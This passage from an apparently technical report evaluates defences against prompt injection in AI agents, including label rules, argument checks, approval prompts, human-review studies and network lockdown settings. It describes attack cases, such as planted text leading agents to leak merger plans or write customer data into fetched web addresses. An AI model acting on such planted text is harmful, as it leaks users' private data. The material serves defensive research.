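Checking individual arguments nearly doubled the number of completed tasks with almost no loss of security. This is the best evidence that most of the tasks lost under these rules are lost because labels spread across the whole context. An agent without the rules still completed many more tasks.

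Palumbo and colleagues' software, FORGE, can also express Willison's lethal trifecta as a single rule:

$$\text{Deny}(a) \Leftarrow \text{ExternalSend}(a) \wedge \text{Tainted}(a) \wedge \text{HasSecret}(a).$$

The rule blocks any action that sends data outside and depends on both untrusted text and private data. In a small test with a planted instruction, an agent with only a warning in its prompt sent confidential merger plans to the attacker in all five trials. The rule blocked the attack in all five, and the agent still completed its ordinary task.

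AgentDojo probably overstates how well systems that plan everything in advance perform. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan. They wrote 60 tasks that all require this and in which outside text contains useful instructions, such as a login prompt on a checkout page. CaMeL completed far fewer of these tasks than an undefended agent. It also fell short when Summers and colleagues tested it on the same benchmark. An assistant that has to follow up on whatever it finds would therefore perform much worse with CaMeL.

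Agents that operate a computer through its screen are harder still. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) describes a system in which a planner writes a program with branches for everything the agent might encounter. The plans averaged 41 tool calls, compared with about 5 for CaMeL on AgentDojo, and the system kept at most 57% of the performance of frontier models. Planted text couldn't add new actions, but a fake cookie notice could steer the agent down an existing branch and onto a hostile site. Label policies offer little protection here because the same click could log in, delete a file or open an advertisement.

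Most of these security figures come from attacks that existed before the defence did. Narisetty and colleagues point out that defences inside the model also had near-zero reported attack success rates, until Nasr and colleagues tailored attacks to twelve of them and succeeded more than 90% of the time against most. Narisetty and colleagues also tailored an attack to Progent, which checks each tool call against fixed rules but doesn't track labels. That attack succeeded 2.6% of the time, while ordinary attacks succeeded 4.2% of the time, down from 25.8% without Progent. This is encouraging, but they tested a single attack template on a small model.

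An attacker may find it easier to exploit a wrong label than to defeat the check. If an employee pastes a stranger's email into a request, the harness will usually treat it as the employee's own words. Narisetty and colleagues warn that in the deployed form of FIDES, unlabeled data counts as trusted. A company should reverse that default, so that a developer who forgets a label causes a refused call instead of a leak. It should also label fields separately, since a customer record may contain both the company's own data and comments typed by the customer.

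### Environment Steering

*Environment Steering*, by Summers and colleagues, checks a tool call's arguments against recorded data instead of trying to work out everything that influenced the model. Its software records the user's request and every tool's inputs and outputs as database tables, and treats a new tool call as a proposed row. Before the call runs, rules compare its arguments with rows from permitted sources. For example, when a shopping agent reorders an item, the product number has to match one in the user's order history, so a number from a planted advertisement fails the check.

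This avoids the spreading problem for values that software can match exactly, such as product numbers and email addresses, but it works less well for free text. To keep an agent from revealing another patient's social security number, one of the paper's rules searches the reply for that number. A disguised number would get past this search, as it would any filter for known values.

Summers and colleagues tested the system on four benchmarks and averaged the results over up to five open models. Attack success fell from 30–74% without a defence to 0.2–14% with the system. The largest rise in task success was 12.7 percentage points, on AgentDojo's office tasks. On *AgentDyn*, one model completed 61% of tasks and no attack succeeded.

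Task success can rise because the refusals are informative. When a call breaks a rule, the software returns the rule, an explanation, the relevant records and the sources the model may take a safe value from. The model then has to write a database command that draws the value from one of those sources. In the sales example, a refusal could direct the model to the table of account teams, where it could pick the right team. When the software instead reported only that the model had violated a security policy, task success on *AgentDyn* was 10.5 points lower than the undefended agent's.

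The rules are less reliable than the software that enforces them. Claude Opus 4.8 wrote most of them, using a few examples that the researchers had corrected. Some rules were too strict, which caused one model to complete fewer AgentDojo tasks. When a hostile instruction and a necessary fact appear in the same document, the system also asks a language model whether the text contains an injection. An attacker may be able to fool that check, and retries give a misled model more chances to get past it. Retries are safer when the rule requires an exact match, because the model can only choose another permitted value.

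### Recipients and page visits

Summers and colleagues' instructions for writing the shopping rules are much stricter about recipients than about web pages. Every tool that sends data or money to a particular party needs a rule, even if the task doesn't need the tool. If the user named a recipient, the rule permits only that one. If the recipient has to come from a document, such as an account number on a bill, the value must appear in the document and pass the injection check. Otherwise the rule blocks every call.

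If the user names an address or site, the rule for a tool that opens web pages permits only that address or site. If the user names none, the tool gets no rule. An agent rarely needs to email someone the user never mentioned, but browsing consists largely of following links that nobody could have listed beforehand, so blocking unknown addresses would make many tasks impossible. Under the instructions, a separate layer handles those addresses by comparing hosts or asking a model to judge. Comparing hosts has the weaknesses of a site list, and asking a model has those of a filter.

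The sales assistant is fairly safe under these instructions when the employee supplies the supplier's web address. But if the employee asks whether any supplier has raised its prices, no rule covers the page tool, and a misled model can write the phone number into an address. The instructions also exempt search tools, on the grounds that reading and searching do no harm. Notion's search tool is a counterexample, because it accepted a full web address and fetched it. FIDES has a similar gap, since its list of guarded tools includes those that post to a web page or download a file, but none that only read a page.

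A company can close much of this gap by treating each fetch as a message to the site's owner and applying the reader rule to the address. If the harness copies a link unchanged from a public page, anyone may read it and the fetch can proceed. If the model composes an address after reading the customer's record, the address carries the record's label and the harness refuses the fetch. The recipient rule would have to be looser for fetches, because a link on an untrusted page is untrusted data that sets the destination. An attacker could then still offer the model a set of links and learn from its choice, so the company would also need to cap the number of fetches.

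## When should a person approve a request, and when should the channel be closed?

Even with labels and address checks, software can't judge some requests, such as a search for a part number on a supplier's site. The harness can refuse such a request or ask the employee to approve it. The company can also remove the assistant's ability to send such requests.

### What an approval prompt has to show

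Until August 2025, the agent in the code editor Zed fetched web pages without asking. *Require confirmation for fetch tool* (Irwin, 2025) changed a few lines of the editor's code so that each fetch waits for the user's approval. Irwin made the change because a misled agent could put private code or access keys from the conversation into the address. The approval prompt shows the complete address, so the user can check where the request will go and whether the address contains anything it shouldn't.

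Asking a user to approve a request works only if the user can interpret the address. OpenAI's warning for unverified links is more helpful because it mentions that the address may contain data from the conversation. If something looks wrong, OpenAI suggests asking ChatGPT for another source or a summary instead. But the user still has to work out which part of the address, if any, is private.

A prompt for the sales assistant could give the full destination, the data that would leave and the reason for the request:

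```
Send this to supplier.example?
Address:       https://supplier.example/search?part=4471-B
Data sent:     "4471-B"
Written by:    the assistant, after reading a customer record
Your request:  "What does part 4471-B cost now?"
```

The harness should fill in these lines from its own records, because a misled model may give a misleading explanation. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) shows a Claude Code prompt that described a command as a suggestion from the project's maintainer. The model was repeating a claim that an attacker had planted. Zed now requires its agent to give a reason when it asks for more access, and Zed's *Sandboxing* tells users to decide whether the reason makes sense. This check can expose an honest mistake, but it is weak protection against a false reason that sounds plausible.

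The approval also has to cover only what the prompt displayed. The harness should wait for the user's answer before it looks up the host name, and ask again if the site redirects the request elsewhere. Broader approvals are convenient but risky. According to *Manage approvals and permissions*, a user of Microsoft's code editor, VS Code, can approve a host for one session or permanently. The model can then put any text in the rest of the address without another prompt.

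Some products let a person edit a request as well as approve or reject it. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) describes an option in Amazon's Bedrock Agents for changing an action's parameters before it runs. With this option, the sales employee could delete a phone number from the note and post the rest.

### The study of 1,053 testers

Before making auto mode the default in Claude Code, Anthropic compared it with having people approve each action. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran, and recorded whether the tester approved it.

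The testers refused 143 of the commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic also reports how often only one of the two caught the command, and the rest of this table follows from those figures.

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught only six of the 116 commands that auto mode missed. Adding a person's approval to every automatic check would therefore have raised the share of commands stopped only from 89.0% to 89.6%, and would have caused constant interruptions.

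The study is weaker evidence about web requests because Anthropic gives no separate result for them. A fetch with a phone number in its address looks much more ordinary than a clearly dangerous command, so people might catch even fewer. On the other hand, the testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose. The 89% may not apply to web requests either. Auto mode's classifier doesn't see the results of earlier tool calls, so it could miss a customer's phone number that came from one.

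Anthropic also had a commercial interest in the outcome, although a gap this large is hard to dismiss for commands of this kind. In real use, among sessions that Anthropic's safety system had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. This evidence is weaker because users had chosen their own mode and a model graded the harm.

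### Fewer prompts or different reviewers

Anthropic takes the results as a reason to stop using people as routine reviewers. In October 2026, it announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, and 62% of them have at some point turned off permission checks or chosen "don't ask again" for shell commands. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found a similar pattern in 290 user reports, with automatic approval contributing to 80 and uninformative prompts to 31.

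The same results can support keeping human approval but using it rarely. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. In a simulation, *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) found that sending more actions to a reviewer who tires can lead to a worse outcome than sending fewer.

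Fatigue is only part of the problem, because testers approved about 83% of the dangerous commands even early in a session. The 39% figure is also ambiguous, since many users probably reject a plan because they want the work done differently.

Clearer wording doesn't solve the problem either. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, asked 113 people from outside the software industry to supervise a simulated assistant that attempted 18 actions, seven of them outside the scope of its task. The prompts described each action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved. The 34 people who decided on each action individually still allowed 40% of the out-of-scope ones. Some of these were fairly harmless, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight, which 30 people allowed, and the figure is 32% without that call.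 Twelve people let the assistant read private messages, and seven let it post publicly that the user was travelling.

These rates suggest that a well-written prompt can fail often, but they don't predict how often employees would approve a theft, because no real data was at stake and no attacker was involved.

People in Yan's other groups often approved out-of-scope actions when the software asked them to decide. One group set rules in advance for four types of action, such as spending money or sending information. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, then approved 67% of the out-of-scope actions they were asked about. For another group, a model correctly flagged all seven out-of-scope actions, but participants still approved them 46% of the time. When a check finds a likely leak, the harness should therefore block it instead of asking the user. Claude Code comes close to this, because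 a user who wants to send secrets outside has to leave auto mode or run the command by hand.

Another problem is that web fetches look like reading. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, surveyed software practitioners about permission requests. Almost all (98.1%) were more willing to grant read-only access, and 76.6% looked more carefully at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges. Only 47.7% said they read prompts carefully, and people tend to overstate such habits. A prompt worded "Read this page?" encourages people to overlook the data in the address, so "Send this to supplier.example?" is better.

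Software should handle routine requests and refer a request to a person only when that person has information the software lacks. The sales employee knows whether they wanted the price of part 4471-B, but they probably don't know who can read an unfamiliar site's server log, so that question should go to an administrator.

A company can also test whether its reviewers pay attention. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) suggests planting known errors and counting how many of them reviewers catch. It also recommends rotating reviewers and having requests approved by someone who doesn't benefit from the result. An employee waiting for a note has an obvious reason to click "yes". Requiring a second reviewer for every note would be too slow, but it would be reasonable for an unusual message that sends customer data outside the company.

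### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

Closing the channel avoids these judgements. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced an optional setting of this kind on 13 February, initially for organisations such as large companies, schools and healthcare providers. OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts and smaller businesses on 4 June. Ordinary software enforces the setting's limits, so they don't depend on the model recognising an attack.

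OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the current help page, lists what changes.

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored copies of pages only, which may be missing or out of date |
| Images | ChatGPT may not display them in ordinary replies or retrieve them from the web |
| Deep Research and agent mode | Off |
| Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing space | Users can't give it network access |
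| File downloads for data analysis | Off, though users can still upload files |
| Connected apps on personal accounts | No live access or changes that conflict with the mode's protections |
| Connected apps in managed workspaces | The administrator chooses |

When the model reads stored copies of pages, no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network. The model can still choose which page to read, but the site's owner doesn't see the choice, so the method ZombieAgent used to leak data doesn't work.

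Instructions planted in a stored page or an uploaded file could still make ChatGPT's answer wrong, or lead the model to misuse an app that the administrator has left on. OpenAI therefore advises administrators against enabling untrusted apps, or actions whose effects an outsider might see. One such action is posting customer notes to a chat channel that a supplier can read. If only trusted colleagues can read the channel, OpenAI classes the action as medium risk.

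Lockdown Mode doesn't affect network access in Codex. On a personal account, the user can turn the mode off for a single chat, so the decision is again made by someone in the middle of a task. In a managed workspace, an owner has to remove the user from the restricted role to restore access.

OpenAI doesn't guarantee that the mode stops every leak. In November 2026, TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported that the security company Check Point had found a way around it, which OpenAI has since fixed.

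OpenAI describes the intended users as a small, "highly security-conscious" group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and says most people don't need it. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomes the design, arguing that outward communication is by far the easiest of the lethal trifecta's three conditions to restrict without making an assistant much less useful. He also infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a sufficiently determined attacker.

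OpenAI says in its announcement that some network features carry risks the industry hasn't fully addressed, and it labels those features "Elevated Risk". The defaults, including the index check, still provide some protection, but OpenAI evidently doesn't consider them enough for everyone.

Willison's broader argument is strongest for an assistant that reads and answers, because someone who loses live browsing can still get a summary of a stored page. The sales assistant also has to send a note, so the company can't close every channel, but it can turn off live fetching and keep a narrow webhook.

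### Network settings in other products

Other vendors offer similar controls, mostly for programming agents or developers. They differ in what happens by default and which tools they cover.

| Product | Network control | Main gap |
|---|---|---|
| Codex | A switch for internet access, a list of domains and a choice of request types | "Full Access" uses the internet without asking |
| Zed | Blocks terminal commands and fetches until the user approves a host or all hosts | Other parts of the editor can still connect |
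| VS Code | An optional sandbox restricts the network for terminal commands | It doesn't cover every tool |
| Anthropic's developer fetch tool | Absent unless the developer adds it, with an optional list of domains | The list covers only this tool |

Since Irwin's fix, Zed has begun using the operating system to enforce the network block on terminal commands, so a program the model writes can't skip the prompt. On Windows, however, Zed can't limit a sandboxed command to particular hosts, so the user has to approve access to the whole network or none of it. Users can also remove most of the prompts with a single setting that approves most tool actions automatically, according to Zed's *Tool Permissions*.

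A closed network can make it safer to skip approval prompts. In VS Code, the "Allow all" level skips them, but the sandbox, if enabled, still restricts terminal commands. The agent can then work without interruptions inside a limit it can't change. The drawback, as Anthropic points out, is that someone has to configure each new capability that needs the network.

As with Rovo's web search setting, an administrator should test whether any such switch really covers every tool.

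### Choosing by data and task

The right control depends on what the assistant can read and how widely it has to browse.

| Data the assistant can read | A few known sites are enough | The task needs the open web |
|---|---|---|
| Public or harmless if disclosed | Ordinary fetching | Ordinary fetching with automatic review |
| Private business records | Exact addresses on a closed list, with a cap on fetches | A separate browsing assistant without the records |
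| Access keys, health records or payment details | Stored copies of pages, with no live requests | A separate browsing assistant, and a person who checks what passes between the two |

The sales company could use stored copies too. An ordinary program could download the catalogues of the company's twelve suppliers every night, and the assistant would read only the copies. The downloads would follow the same schedule whatever the assistant had read, so they would reveal nothing about customers. Prices could be a day old, but an employee who needs a current one can open the supplier's site in their own browser.

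If staff also need to research unfamiliar suppliers, they can use a browsing assistant that has no customer records and copy its findings into the sales assistant. The copied text may contain a planted instruction, but the sales assistant would have no live fetch tool and could post only to the team's channel. If an employee wants to send a note outside the team, the harness can show them the recipient and the full text before sending it.
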